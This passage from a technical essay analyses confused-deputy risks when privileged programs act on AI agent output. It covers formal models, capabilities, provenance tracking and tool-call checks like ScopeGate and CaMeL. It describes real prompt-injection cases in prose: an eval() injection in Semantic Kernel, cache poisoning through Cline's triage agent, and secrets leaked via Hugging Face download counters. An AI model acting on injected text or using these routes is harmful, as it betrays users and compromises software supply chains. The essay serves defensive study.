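To apply the 2016 definition, an analyst can put the agent's output in the hole, since injected text might lead the agent to write any valid record. Both conditions then fail, because different records lead to different payments and the agent cannot make payments itself. They would fail even if the dispatcher checked every request and paid only refunds that the company owed, because the agent would still influence which refunds were paid. The company would have to endorse the payment step, and then only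 the caps in the dispatcher's code, not the definition, would limit what it pays.

### When nobody attacks

An agent can also misuse authority by mistake. Siu and colleagues describe a user who asks a cooking assistant to find a recipe and order the ingredients. The recipe recommends a particular brand of pan, and the assistant adds a new skillet to the order. They call this task drift, because no outside source told the assistant to buy the skillet.

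In the support example, the agent might misread order 1001 as 1007, so the dispatcher refunds the wrong customer. This is not a confused-deputy attack, because nobody was trying to get the dispatcher to act for them. The dispatcher still supplies the authority for the payment, as it would in an attack.

Some of the definitions still cover these mistakes. The four conditions in *Proof-of-Continuity* do not mention an attacker or anyone's intentions. All four hold for the refund if the email counts as a request to the dispatcher, because the customer with order 1001 has no right to refund order 1007, the dispatcher does, and the customer's request led to the payment. The skillet purchase does not meet them, because the user is free to buy one. It could meet the definition in *Beyond Proof of Possession* if the request carried only the right to buy ingredients and the assistant had separate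 access to the user's payment card.

The 2016 definition classifies programs rather than individual incidents. If the analyst leaves out the hole that represents the attacker, because no attacker exists, the support system is trivially free from attacks. The system fails the definition when the analyst puts the agent's output in the hole, even if nobody ever attacks it. The analysis then already allows for the mistaken record.

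## Why capabilities stop some of these attacks and not others

Capabilities stop attacks in which the attacker picks the object that the deputy acts on. They do not stop an attacker who influences what the deputy does to an object it can already use, and agent output often affects downstream programs in this second way. The loss of the billing file convinced Hardy that capabilities were necessary, and later writers often presented them as the cure for confused deputies in general.

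### The argument for capabilities

Hardy sketched the argument and Miller and colleagues set it out more fully. It has four premises:

1. A request to act on an object must designate that object somehow.
2. In a capability system, the requester designates an object by passing a capability for it. Knowing the object's name is not enough.
3. Nobody can forge a capability, so the requester can pass only one that it already holds.
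4. Anyone who holds a capability may use it.

A requester can therefore point the deputy only at objects the requester could have used without the deputy's help. This restriction would have protected Tymshare's billing file.

Miller and colleagues call the second premise "no designation without authority". They note that it also rules out ambient authority, because every request then carries the authority it relies on. Ruling out ambient authority alone would not be enough. They give the example of a deputy that tries every key on a ring until a door opens. This deputy can go wrong just as the compiler did, because it doesn't keep track of what each key is for. A capability that arrives with a request is easier to use correctly, since the request shows what the capability is for.

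They conclude only that a "common type" of confused deputy problem cannot occur, in which a malicious party designates a resource it is not supposed to access, and they accept that no security model can prevent people from writing bad programs. But they define a confused deputy more broadly, as one that someone has manipulated into using its authority inappropriately, so their argument does not cover everything that meets their definition.

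The second premise can also fail inside a capability system. In the mailing-list thread *Confused deputy*, Karp (2026) asked whether anyone had proved that such a system cannot contain a confused deputy. William ML Leslie replied that it can, because a deputy can put its capabilities in a lookup table and let the client choose one. The client then designates an object with plain data, and the deputy supplies the authority. Mark Miller answered that the guarantee applies to a deputy that uses only capabilities to designate objects. He called this a severe restriction that many normal deputies do not meet, though he thought most of them were safe anyway.

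The support dispatcher would be a deputy of the kind Leslie described. Suppose the company rewrote it in a capability language and gave it a separate capability for each of the 10,000 orders. If the dispatcher kept using the order number in each record to look up the right capability, the agent could still choose any order.

Miller's rule of thumb is that a deputy is probably safe if it does not use rights amplification, in which a program combines two references to get access that neither gives alone. The usual example is a sealed box that contains a capability and opens only with a matching unsealer. In an earlier thread, *Testing for a confused deputy vulnerability* (Karp, 2019), Christopher Lemmer Webber warned about deputies that keep a bucket of unsealers and try them all. An attacker could give such a deputy a box that the attacker cannot open, and the deputy would open it and use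 the contents. Kevin Reid replied that sealed boxes are safe if the deputy keeps track of what each unsealer means, as the ring of keys also required.

### Three attacks that capabilities do not stop

Rajani and colleagues tested the argument in the small language they used for their definition, giving it two alternative sets of rules for running programs. Under the access-control rules, a step may hold any reference, and the system checks the step's rights only when it writes. Under the capability rules, the system checks every value that a step computes or reads. If the value is a write reference that the step has no right to use, the program halts.

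Under both sets of rules, a step can provably write only to objects it has the right to write to. Confused-deputy attacks are still possible because the deputy has the right to make the harmful write.

The capability rules stop the attack on the simplified compiler because the attacker cannot pass the compiler a reference to a file the attacker may not write to.

In the next three programs, the attacker wants to change `ledger` but has no right to write to it. The attacker can write to `inbox`, `flag` and `slot`. In the first program, the attacker controls the value that the deputy writes:

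`⊥{ • } ∘ ⊤{ ledger := !inbox }`

Suppose `ledger` starts at 0. It ends at 42 if the attacker puts 42 in `inbox`, and at 41 if the attacker puts 41 there. The attacker controls the result and could not have produced it alone, so both conditions in the definition fail. The capability rules do not prevent this, because the attacker used only a reference to `inbox`, and 42 is not a reference. Rajani and colleagues compare this to SQL injection, in which a web server passes an attacker's text to a database that the attacker cannot reach.

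In the second program, the attacker controls which branch the deputy takes:

`⊥{ • } ∘ ⊤{ if !flag then ledger := 41 else ledger := 42 }`

The programmer wrote both numbers, and nothing the attacker supplies is copied into `ledger`, but the attacker still decides which number ends up there. This is implicit influence, where data affects which action a program takes without appearing in the result.

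The third program resembles the compiler:

`⊥{ • } ∘ ⊤{ !slot := !inbox }`

The deputy copies the contents of `inbox` to whatever object `slot` refers to. Suppose `slot` already holds a write reference to `ledger` when the program starts. The attacker could not have put that reference there under the capability rules, but now only has to write 42 to `inbox`, and the deputy copies it into `ledger`.

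Rajani and colleagues distinguish explicit from implicit designation. In explicit designation, the attacker gives the deputy its reference to the attacked object, as happened with the compiler. In implicit designation, the deputy already has the reference, in its code or in memory, and the attacker influences what it writes through that reference. Capabilities prevent attacks by explicit designation but not by implicit designation.

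Some people would not call all of these programs confused deputies. In the 2026 thread, Karp described a confused deputy as one that uses its permissions on a resource that somebody else designated. In the first two programs, the attacker does not designate `ledger` in the ordinary sense. If the term covers only cases where the attacker picks the object, the traditional argument holds, but the attacker can still corrupt the ledger.

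### When capabilities are enough

A deputy can come to hold a write reference to an object in three ways. The programmer can put the reference in the deputy's code, the deputy can read it from memory, or the attacker can pass it to the deputy. The capability rules prevent the attacker from passing a reference to a protected object, meaning one that the attacker wants to change but may not write to. To guarantee that a program is free from attacks, Rajani and colleagues had to assume that the deputy never gets such a reference in the other two ways either. Their theorem about capabilities has two assumptions:

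- Outside endorsed steps, the deputy's code contains no write reference to a protected object.
- No object in memory holds such a reference when the program starts.

If both are true, the program is free from confused-deputy attacks under the capability rules, apart from any influence the programmer has endorsed. The proof shows that no unendorsed step gets a write reference to a protected object, so those steps can't change any protected object, whatever the attacker does.

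The theorem thus protects objects by assuming that the deputy cannot change them. Rajani and colleagues acknowledge that these restrictions make the language useless for almost all practical purposes. Even Hardy's improved compiler does not satisfy them, because it holds a capability for the statistics file, which customers have no right to change, and the statistics it records depend on each customer's program. Its programmers would have to endorse that step, and the theorem would then no longer cover it.

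### Tracking where values came from

Rajani and colleagues also studied two methods that track provenance to prevent attacks. Both start from the access-control rules and label every value the program computes.

Each label is a principal. A constant in the program's code gets the highest label, ⊤. When a step reads an object, the result's label cannot be higher than the object's owner. A low label therefore means that someone with little authority may have influenced the value.

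The simpler method, explicit provenance tracking, checks these labels when a step tries to write to an object. As under ordinary access control, the step's principal must rank at least as high as the object's owner. Unless the step is endorsed, the labels on the value and the reference must also rank at least that high.

Suppose `ledger` belongs to the highest principal, and `inbox`, `flag` and `slot` belong to the lowest. In the first program, the deputy reads 42 from `inbox`, so the value has label ⊥. That label is too low for `ledger`, so the system halts the program. In the program that writes through `slot`, the reference to `ledger` also gets label ⊥ when the deputy reads it. The system would halt that program even if the deputy were writing a constant.

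The branch attack still works. The numbers 41 and 42 and the reference to `ledger` are all constants, so they have label ⊤, and the check passes whichever branch the attacker chose.

The theorem for explicit tracking keeps the assumption about the deputy's code but weakens the one about memory. References to protected objects may now appear in objects that the attacker can write to, because such a reference gets a low label when the deputy reads it, but they must still not appear in other objects. For example, a starting state in which `slot` refers to `ledger` violates the capability theorem's assumption but is allowed here. Under these assumptions, explicit tracking gives the same guarantee as the capability theorem.

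The assumption about code is needed to exclude the branch attack, but it also excludes the program that copies `inbox` to `ledger`, even though the label check stops the attack there. Explicit tracking can therefore prevent some attacks in programs that its theorem does not cover.

Full provenance tracking adds a label for the program's current position. The label starts at ⊤. When the program enters the body of an `if` or a `while`, the system lowers the label to account for the data in the condition, then restores the old label when the program leaves the body. An unendorsed step may write to an object only if the position label also ranks at least as high as the object's owner. In the branch attack, the condition depends on `flag`, so the position label falls to ⊥ and the system blocks both assignments to `ledger`.

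Under full tracking, every program in the language is free from confused-deputy attacks, whatever the starting memory, again apart from endorsed influence. Rajani and colleagues prove this by showing that full tracking enforces a form of noninterference, which is a stronger property. However, explicit tracking can be implemented far more efficiently.

All three methods prevent attacks by halting the program, and the definition covers only runs that finish. An attacker who cannot change the ledger may still stop the deputy from working. If a dispatcher halted whenever it read a suspicious record, one hostile email could delay everyone's refunds.

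### Which harmless programs each method stops

Each method also halts some programs that contain no attack. Rajani and colleagues give an example in which a principal M copies data between two objects:

`M{ summary := !notes }`

M may write to both objects, but the owner of `summary` ranks above the owner of `notes`. The attacker has the same rank as M, so it can write to `summary` directly and doesn't need a deputy. The capability rules let this program finish, but explicit tracking halts it because the value comes from a lower-ranked object, regardless of who the attacker is.

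Other programs run under explicit tracking but not under the capability rules. Suppose M may write to `slot` but not to `ledger`, and runs this step:

`M{ slot := ledger }`

The step stores a reference to `ledger` without writing to `ledger` itself. The capability rules halt the program as soon as M computes the reference. Rajani and colleagues use this example to show that access control is more permissive than capabilities. Explicit tracking also allows the step, because M may write to `slot` and the reference is a constant with label ⊤.

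One example compares explicit tracking directly with capabilities, using a deputy that always writes 1 to `ledger`. The attacker cannot affect the result, and explicit tracking lets the program finish, but the capability rules halt it if the attacker's commands even mention `ledger`. This example is less clean because the deputy's code contains a reference to `ledger`, which violates an assumption of both theorems.

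Full tracking is stricter than explicit tracking. If M sets `summary` to 41 or 42 depending on the contents of `notes`, explicit tracking allows it and full tracking does not. The table shows what happens to each program.

| Program | Capabilities | Explicit tracking | Full tracking |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attack: the attacker names the compiler's output file | Halted | Halted | Halted |
| Attack: the attacker controls the value written | Succeeds | Halted | Halted |
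| Attack: the attacker controls the branch taken | Succeeds | Succeeds | Halted |
| Attack: the deputy writes the attacker's data through a stored reference | Succeeds | Halted | Halted |
| Harmless: M copies `notes` to `summary` | Runs | Halted | Halted |
| Harmless: M stores a reference that it may not write through | Halted | Runs | Runs |
| Harmless: M chooses a constant for `summary` based on `notes` | Runs | Runs | Halted |

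### A capability for the sender's own order

Suppose the company in the support example replaces the order number in each record with a capability, and the dispatcher still refunds at most $200 in total on any one order. A trusted mail program identifies the customer who sent each email and starts a fresh agent to handle it. The program gives the agent's harness a capability to request a refund on that customer's order and on no other. The model still writes only text, so it chooses the route and the harness attaches the capability to the record. (How a queue could carry a capability is a separate problem.)

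One hostile email could eventually cost the company $2,000,000 if the agent uses order numbers, but at most $200 if it uses the capability. A customer who writes "refund order 2002" gains nothing, because the agent has no capability for order 2002. The agent also can't refund order 1007 by misreading 1001.

This protection depends on the mail program identifying the sender correctly and on starting a fresh agent for each email. If a single agent kept the capabilities from all the emails it had handled, injected text could lead it to use the wrong capability, as in Leslie's lookup table. The protection also doesn't reduce the total the company could lose. If each of the 10,000 orders belonged to a different customer and every customer made a false claim, the company could still pay out $2,000,000.

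Now suppose the customer with order 1001 received the parcel but writes that it never arrived. The agent believes the email and chooses `refund`, and the dispatcher pays $200. The customer designated only their own order, so the capability worked as intended. What the customer controlled was the branch that the dispatcher took:

`if !route = refund then pay(200)`

Explicit tracking would allow this payment, because the amount is a constant in the dispatcher's code. Full tracking would block it, along with every honest claim, because the route depends on a customer's email. To pay any refunds, the company would have to endorse the payment step, and full tracking would then no longer prevent undeserved refunds. True and false claims come from the same kind of source and take the same path through the program, so provenance labels cannot distinguish them.

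Reid discussed a similar case in the 2019 thread that Karp started. A student falsely reports that another student is being disruptive, and the teacher silences the accused student. Reid called the teacher a confused deputy "of the ordinary human type". He said that treating the case as a formal security bug would require a specification of what the teacher should do, and that no such specification can exist where people expect the teacher to use judgment.

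The company can write such a specification for some refunds. For example, the dispatcher could pay a claim for a missing parcel only if the carrier has no record of delivery. It would then rely on evidence the customer does not control. This check would not help with a claim that the goods arrived broken if the customer's word is the only evidence.

### The reply from the capability side

Supporters of capabilities can answer that the 2016 model leaves out much of what makes capabilities useful. Miller and Shapiro had made a similar objection to earlier work, arguing that researchers had wrongly "proven" some security policies impossible in capability systems because they looked only at who had access to what. Those proofs left out small programs such as the Caretaker, whose behavior is part of the protection.

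The language that Rajani and colleagues studied has no such programs. A reference gives direct access to a stored value, and anyone who holds a write reference can write anything through it. The researchers acknowledge that their model leaves out the encapsulated objects found in object-capability languages. In one of those languages, the company could give the dispatcher a refund object for each order instead of direct access to its bank account. Each object would have a single method that checks the delivery record and never pays more than $200 in total. Even a badly written dispatcher holding only these objects could not exceed the limit on any order.

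Programmers can also split a deputy so that each part serves one client or purpose. Webber gave the example of a bot that rewrites blog posts in mixed capital letters, posts the result as a comment, and sends a copy to whoever asked for it. A blog's owner lets the bot read every post, including private ones, so an outsider can point it at a private post and receive a copy. Reid suggested running a separate instance of the bot for each grant of access, so that the outsider couldn't call the instance that can read the private posts. Webber doubted that users could keep track of so many instances, and suggested showing them a single bot that separates each user's work internally. A support agent avoids much of this difficulty, because the mail program can start the right instance without asking the customer to choose.

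Splitting programs and narrowing their access does not settle how each deputy must behave. Spiessens's doctoral thesis, *Patterns of Safe Collaboration* (2007), used an automated tool to work this out for a deputy like Hardy's compiler. The model contained a client, the client's file, the deputy and the deputy's file. The deputy had to be able to write the client's output to the client's file but never to its own. The tool searched for the fewest restrictions on the deputy's behavior that would guarantee this, without assuming that the client or either file was well behaved.

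Spiessens found seven things that the deputy must not do. For example, it must not return its own file to the client, because the client could then name that file as the output. Less obviously, it must not send its own file to the client's file, because the client's "file" could be a hostile program with the same interface. When Spiessens assumed that the deputy's file was an ordinary file that could hold only data, the list fell to four. Capabilities made it possible to avoid confusion, but the deputy's programmer still had to follow these rules.

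In the 2026 thread, Miller recommended the thesis as a place to look for formal proofs about confused deputies, and Karp replied that its section on the subject was what he had been looking for. But the property Spiessens checked concerns which file the deputy uses for the client's output. The model does not track the values the deputy writes to its own file, so the result does not rule out attacks in which the client influences those values.

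The refund object has the same limitation. It is itself a deputy, because it can access the company's money and acts on a customer's claim. The capability rules do not ensure that it checks the delivery record correctly. But it is much smaller than the dispatcher and the agent. To confirm the $200 limit, an engineer would have to examine only the refund object and the system that enforces the capability rules.

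## How privileged programs come to act on agent output

The support dispatcher plainly acts on agent output when it reads a record and pays a refund, but other privileged programs do so less visibly. A program may run the output as code, use it to choose a file or an account, or use it to decide between actions its programmers wrote. It may also read the output much later, from storage it shares with the agent. One attack can combine several of these routes, and a defence against one often doesn't stop another. For example, a strict output type can keep commands out of a field, but a one-word answer can still trigger a payment.

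### Output that runs as code or a query

Microsoft (2026) described two flaws its researchers found in Semantic Kernel, its open-source framework for building agents. The framework's developers have since fixed both.

One flaw turned a search term into a program. The researchers built a demonstration agent that finds hotels. When a user asks for hotels in Paris, the model calls a search tool with the city set to `Paris`, and the tool writes a line of Python to filter its records:

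`lambda x: x.city == 'Paris'`

The tool put the model's value between the quotation marks in this line without checking it, then passed the line to `eval()`, a Python function that runs text as code. A value containing a quotation mark could end the city name early, and Python would run whatever came next. With a single injected prompt, the researchers started the calculator on the machine that hosted the agent.

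The framework's developers had foreseen this danger. Before running a filter, the software checked that it was a single expression of the expected kind, searched it for names on a list of dangerous operations, and disabled Python's built-in functions. The researchers got past all three precautions by wrapping their code in a valid expression, using dangerous names that were not on the list, and starting from an ordinary Python object, through which code can reach the rest of the language without the built-in functions. The repaired version mostly lists what is allowed instead of what is banned. It accepts only approved kinds of expression, such as comparisons and arithmetic, and the only variable a filter may name is the record it is testing.

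The tool required the city to be a string, but this did not stop the attack because a malicious program is also a string. The records in the support example prevent such an attack because an order number and one of five fixed words cannot contain a command. If the company added a free-text comment and the dispatcher pasted it into a database query, anyone who could steer the agent might be able to do whatever the dispatcher's database account allows. The attacker's commands would then run with the deputy's authority, rather than the attacker's own as in the formal model, so the attacker would not be limited to the actions that the deputy's programmers had written.

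### Output that selects a target

The other flaw in Semantic Kernel closely resembles the one at Tymshare. The framework can run an agent's Python code in a sandbox, an isolated environment in the cloud with its own file system. Helper functions on the host, the machine where the agent runs, copy files into and out of the sandbox. In the .NET version, the developers had accidentally made the download helper a tool the model could call. This let the model choose where on the host to save a file, and nothing checked the path.

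Microsoft's researchers used injected instructions to make the agent write a script inside the sandbox, where it could do no harm, and then save it in the host's Windows Startup folder. Windows runs the contents of that folder the next time the user signs in. The upload helper also accepted any path on the host, so an attacker could have made the agent copy private login keys from the host into the sandbox.

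As with the compiler, one party supplied a path as plain data and a program with more rights opened it. The developers stopped offering the download helper to the model and, for programmers who call it from their own code, added a check that the path is in a permitted directory. A capability would also have prevented the attack. If the host had opened one download folder and given the helper access to only that folder, the model could have controlled what was saved but not which folder it was saved in.

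### Output that decides a branch

Sometimes the agent output that a program acts on is only a verdict. Claude Code and Codex, the coding agents from Anthropic and OpenAI, have modes that run commands the agent judges safe without asking the user. In July 2026, Heidy Khlaaf and Boyan Milanov of the AI Now Institute showed that an attacker could manipulate this judgment with text hidden in an open-source library. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn*, both agents judged a malicious script in the library to be safe and ran it, although the user had asked only for a security review.

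The attacker supplied the script, but the verdict determined whether the agent ran it or stopped to ask. This is the branch attack from the formal model. A narrower type would not prevent it, because the harness must accept "safe" as a valid answer. Designers can still limit what a "safe" verdict allows, for instance by running approved commands in a sandbox that holds no credentials.

### Output left in shared state: the Cline case

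On February 17, 2026, someone published an unauthorized version of a command-line tool made by Cline, whose open-source coding agent had passed 5 million installs. The events behind it began on December 21, 2025, when Cline's maintainers set up an AI agent to sort issues, the bug reports and requests that people post on a project's GitHub page. *Clinejection* (Khan, 2026) explained how an attacker could get from that agent to the project's releases.

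The agent ran on GitHub Actions, which runs a project's automated jobs, called workflows, on temporary machines. Whenever anyone with a GitHub account opened an issue, the triage workflow started Claude, put the issue's title into the prompt and let the model run shell commands. According to *Post-mortem*, Cline's account of the incident (Rizwan, 2026), the workflow could read the repository and write to issues but could not change the code. The only secret it could access directly was a key for Anthropic's API.

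A different workflow published a test version of Cline every night. It held the tokens for publishing to the VS Code Marketplace, OpenVSX and npm, three services from which developers install software. To save time, it restored third-party packages from a cache. GitHub lets every workflow that runs on a repository's default branch read and write that branch's cache, even if its configuration contains nothing about caching. The triage agent and the nightly release therefore shared a cache, although Cline had not given the agent access to the release.

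An attacker could not directly replace the cached files, because a workflow cannot overwrite an existing cache entry and the triage workflow lacked permission to delete one. However, GitHub discards the least recently used entries once a repository's cache grows past 10 GB. Until November 2025 it did this once a day, but it now does so immediately. An attacker who controlled the triage agent could fill the cache with junk until GitHub discarded the genuine entries, then store other files under the same keys. That night's release workflow would load those files, and the attacker's code would run in the workflow that held the publishing tokens.

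*Clinejection* (Willison, 2026) explains that the release workflow's cache key included a hash of the file that lists the project's exact dependencies, so an entry for an outdated list would not match. The key identified the packages that an entry was supposed to contain, but it did not depend on the entry's actual contents or on which workflow had stored it. An attacker could compute the key as easily as Cline could.

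An attacker who stole the tokens for the test version could have published a production release, because the VS Code Marketplace and OpenVSX tie a token to a publisher rather than to one extension, and on npm Cline used the same package for both versions. In the terms used earlier, the triage agent had permission to read code and write to issues, but its authority extended to the software on developers' machines.

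### What Khan showed and what happened later

Khan tested only the start of this chain. He copied Cline's repository, used his own API key, and changed the workflow slightly to record more detail. Each time he opened an issue with a crafted title, Claude installed a package he had chosen, and the package ran his code. He did not poison Cline's cache or take its tokens. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1680* quotes his later statement stressing that he had not conducted overt testing on Cline's own repository. For the remaining steps, he relied on Cline's public workflow files and his experience with the same cache technique in other projects.

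Khan reported the flaw privately to Cline on January 1 and tried several more times to reach the company. After he published his findings on February 9, Cline removed the vulnerable workflows within 30 minutes and began replacing its credentials.

By then someone else may already have used the flaw. Several nightly releases had failed between January 31 and February 3, and the failures showed signs of Cacheract, an open-source cache-poisoning tool that Khan had written. He concluded that someone had apparently poisoned the cache. The triage agent was the most obvious way in, but he could not confirm that the intruder had used it. On February 10 someone emailed him anonymously, claiming to have working npm and OpenVSX credentials for Cline. He told Cline, which replied the next day that it had revoked every old token.

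That was wrong because, as Rizwan explains, the team had deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active. They had checked an npm management page that showed no active tokens, but the page did not display this one. On February 17 a third party used the exposed token to publish version 2.3.0. Apart from the version number, the only change was a script that installed OpenClaw, a legitimate open-source program, on the user's machine. Cline published a clean version about eight hours later. The security company StepSecurity estimated roughly 4,000 downloads in that time, according to Briefly's *Cline CLI 2.3.0 Supply Chain Attack Installed OpenClaw on Developer Systems*.

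The public record therefore shows that someone published the release with a valid token that Cline had meant to revoke, but not how that person got the token. Rizwan's post-mortem explains what an attacker could have done with the cache but gives no evidence, such as logs, that the token was stolen that way. The failed releases and the anonymous email make Khan's route the most likely explanation, but no one has shown that an issue title led to this release.

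Cline had told Khan that its maintainers had to approve production releases, which reduced the exposure. But that approval applied only to Cline's own workflow, and npm accepted a release from anyone who held the token. Cline has since stopped using long-lived npm tokens, so a thief can't keep one for later use. Each npm release now also carries a signed record that links it to a specific workflow run. These changes would not necessarily stop malicious code already running inside the release workflow, which could publish from there and receive a genuine record. Cline also decided to remove the cache from every workflow that handles publishing credentials, which addresses that case more directly.

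### Handoffs between stages of a coding agent

The agent at Cline could run shell commands, but an attacker sometimes needs only the ability to write one file. In August 2026 Elad Meged of Novee Security presented attacks on the coding agents of Anthropic, Google and OpenAI, carried out in the vendors' own repositories under default configurations. Witts (2026), in *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex*, describes a shared pattern in which the product marks something as safe at one stage and a later component uses it with more authority than that decision had allowed for.

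The attack on OpenAI's Codex is the closest to the Cline case. A workflow that looked for duplicate issues ran Codex twice in the same working folder. An attacker could use the first run to write instructions into AGENTS.md, a file Codex reads for guidance about a project. The second run, which had more privileges, then loaded the file as trusted.

In Anthropic's workflow, the harness approved a command because it looked harmless, and a later step published the command's output by default. Meged said in Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* that neither decision was wrong alone, but together they exposed secrets. In Google's Gemini CLI, the operator had configured a limit on what the agent could do, but the software did not enforce it at execution. Google had also removed secrets from the process that ran the agent's commands, but that process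 could still read them from its parent process.

In response, OpenAI split its workflow into isolated jobs. Underhill (2026) reports in *Black Hat 2026* that it also documented AGENTS.md as an untrusted input. Google gave its flaw the maximum severity score of 10.0 and changed how Gemini CLI assigns trust when no person is present to approve actions. Anthropic paid bounties and issued a series of patches. Meged said that each patch closed the hole he had reported but also showed him where to look for the next one. The problem extends beyond these three companies. SC Media's *AI coding tools vulnerable to malicious GitHub issues* reports that Novee found similar configurations in more than 100 public repositories.

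Meged recommends that harnesses check trust again when a component uses a value, not only when an earlier component approves it. A command that only reads files is no longer harmless if the next step posts the result in public. But the later component can make this check only if it has reliable information about where the value came from. An ordinary text file has no reliable record of which agent run wrote it, so the privileged run of Codex could not distinguish the attacker's instructions from the project's own. OpenAI's isolated jobs avoid this problem because the two runs no longer share the file.

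### When a well-typed argument counts as authorization

Agent frameworks are built around a similar handoff, between the model that writes a tool call and the software that carries it out. In a June 2026 audit, Mellafe Zuvic examined only whether frameworks by default check the actual argument values in the model's call against a fixed rule, and refuse the call if the values don't meet the rule or the check itself breaks down.

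The audit covered exact snapshots of the public code, so that others could repeat it:

| Software | Version examined |
|---|---|
| LangChain | commit 00ad96c |
| LangGraph | commit bdb323e |
| LlamaIndex | version 0.14.23, commit 520aa4e |
| Stripe Agent Toolkit | commits 0b4961f and f54c9e6 |

The answer was no in every case. Developers using LangChain can attach callback functions that observe a call, but a callback's return value does not reliably block the call. If the model requests a tool that does not exist, LlamaIndex reports this to the model but does not treat the request as a security event.

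Stripe's toolkit is the most sensitive of the three because it handles payments. An operator can limit which actions the toolkit offers and what its API key may do. Within those limits, the toolkit forwards the amount, currency, customer and other details as the model wrote them. A key that can issue legitimate refunds can therefore also issue one that an attacker requested.

All of these designs in effect treat a well-formed argument as authorized, even though the model fills in the values after reading untrusted text.

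The finding covers default behavior, not applications whose developers have added their own check or required human approval. Mellafe Zuvic did not examine Stripe's remote server, which may apply further rules, and does not describe the results as software vulnerabilities. The frameworks leave authorization to the developers who build on them.

### ScopeGate's five checks

ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's checking layer for tool calls, is meant to fill this gap. No language model takes part in its decisions. For each call, it goes through five stages:

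1. Scope: the operator's policy must list the tool.
2. Authorization: if the policy restricts an argument, the value must belong to the allowed set for that argument.
3. Money ceiling: for payments and refunds, the amount must be a finite number from zero up to a set maximum.
4. Idempotency: where the policy requires it, the call must come with an idempotency key from a trusted source. This is an identifier that lets a payment service recognize a repeated request and carry it out only once.
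5. Default deny: ScopeGate allows a call only if it has passed every other stage, and refuses it if an error occurs along the way.

The operator must set the policy, and no part of it may derive from model output, even indirectly or in advance. Otherwise, injected text that substituted a different account in a tool call could also add that account to the allowed set.

When Mellafe Zuvic sent ScopeGate the payout change that LangChain had carried out, the authorization stage rejected it because the allowed set contained only the merchant's own account. ScopeGate also rejected all of a fixed set of 48 attack inputs, which included account names with invisible or look-alike characters, misspelled tool names, values of the wrong type, unusual amounts and missing idempotency keys.

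In an adaptive test, a language model, GLM-5.2, tried to get past ScopeGate for 40 rounds and learned the reason for each refusal. None of its 29 unauthorized attempts succeeded. Of the other 11 rounds, nine produced malformed calls and two produced harmless calls that ScopeGate allowed. In a separate test, ScopeGate refused none of 10 legitimate calls.

These are small tests by the person who designed the software. Even if the 29 attempts had been independent random trials, zero successes would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 10 percent, at 95 percent confidence. The rule's simplicity is a better reason for confidence. If an account is not in the set and the code compares the two correctly, no wording can get it through. The tests are useful mainly for finding mistakes in the code, such as the early prototype's failure to reject NaN.

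The published algorithm applies the ceiling to each call separately and keeps no running total, so an agent could exceed it in total over several calls if each had a new idempotency key. ScopeGate also protects only actions that pass through it. At Cline, the release workflow loaded its packages from the cache without any tool call from the agent, so a check on the agent's tool calls would not have examined that step.

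### Permitted values chosen for the wrong reason

An allowlist works well in the payout demonstration because only one account is ever correct. Most businesses need longer lists. If a company pays 300 approved suppliers through an agent, one of them could send an invoice with hidden text that leads the agent to pay that supplier for another supplier's work. ScopeGate would allow the payment because the account is on the list and the amount is below the ceiling. The published algorithm also tests each argument separately, so it can check that the supplier is approved and the amount is acceptable, but not that this supplier is owed this amount.

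The support example has the same weakness. All 10,000 order numbers are valid, so an allowlist of orders would let the customer with order 1001 obtain a refund on order 2002. The company could do better by giving each conversation its own policy that permits only the sender's order. If a trusted program set this policy before the model read the email, the policy would restrict the agent much as the capability did in the earlier version of the example, and the agent would be just as exposed to false claims.

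An attacker can also use the choice between permitted values to send information. Claude Code could fetch pages from a list of approved sites without asking the user, and one of them was Hugging Face, where anyone can publish AI models. Witts reports that Meged, in the last round of his work on Anthropic's agent, got secrets out through that site's public download counters. The secret determined which pages on the approved site the agent requested, and anyone could then read the counters.

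A longer or stricter list would not solve this problem in general, because the check only compares a value with the list and has no information about where the agent got the value. An agent might copy a supplier's account number from the company's own payment records or from a stranger's email, and if the number is the same, ScopeGate returns the same result.

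## Interpreters that label values while agent code runs

An interpreter that runs the agent's whole program can record where values came from, which ScopeGate does not do. It attaches a provenance label to every value the program reads, derives labels for any values computed from those, and checks the labels before each tool call. Several research systems combine such an interpreter with a rule about which model may read untrusted text.

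### Two models with separate jobs

Simon Willison proposed the "dual-LLM pattern" in 2023. A privileged model reads the user's request and plans the work, but never reads untrusted material such as emails and web pages. A quarantined model reads that material, but it has no tools and can only return a value. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) names CaMeL and FIDES as two systems that implement the pattern.

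In CaMeL, the privileged model writes its plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. Nikolaou and colleagues give an example, which in simplified form looks like this:

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = ask_quarantined("Extract Bob's email from: " + messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

The privileged model writes all three lines before any part of the system reads the channel. If a message there contains hidden instructions, the quarantined model may follow them, but it can only return an address, so it cannot add a fourth line to the plan.

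It can still return the attacker's address, and the third line would then send the message there. CaMeL is meant to prevent this by labeling the address with the channel it came from, so that the policy function that checks the call can refuse it.

The separation between the models also fails if the plan lets untrusted text choose the actions. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) turned off CaMeL's policy checks and gave it a task that asked the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that turned each instruction into a tool call, so an attacker who changed the file could choose the calls.

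### FIDES: hiding untrusted data from the planner

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a system that keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which a model requests one tool call at a time. Each label marks a value as trusted or untrusted (its integrity) and lists who may read it (its confidentiality). A value computed from two others is untrusted if either of them is, and only people on both lists may read it. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text that combines the two.

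The planning model's conversation has a label too. In a basic agent, a single untrusted email makes the whole conversation untrusted, along with every tool call the model then requests. A policy that allows important actions only from a trusted conversation would block even a message the user had asked the agent to send.

FIDES avoids this by storing the email in a variable and showing the planning model only the variable's name. Suppose a user asks the agent to send their three latest emails to a colleague. The model requests the emails, receives the name `#read_emails_0`, and passes that name to the messaging tool as the message. FIDES then replaces the name with the emails' text. The model has chosen the tool and the recipient without reading the emails, so a policy can require those two choices to be trusted while accepting an untrusted message. If the task requires a summary, the planning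 model can call a quarantined model to write one into another variable.

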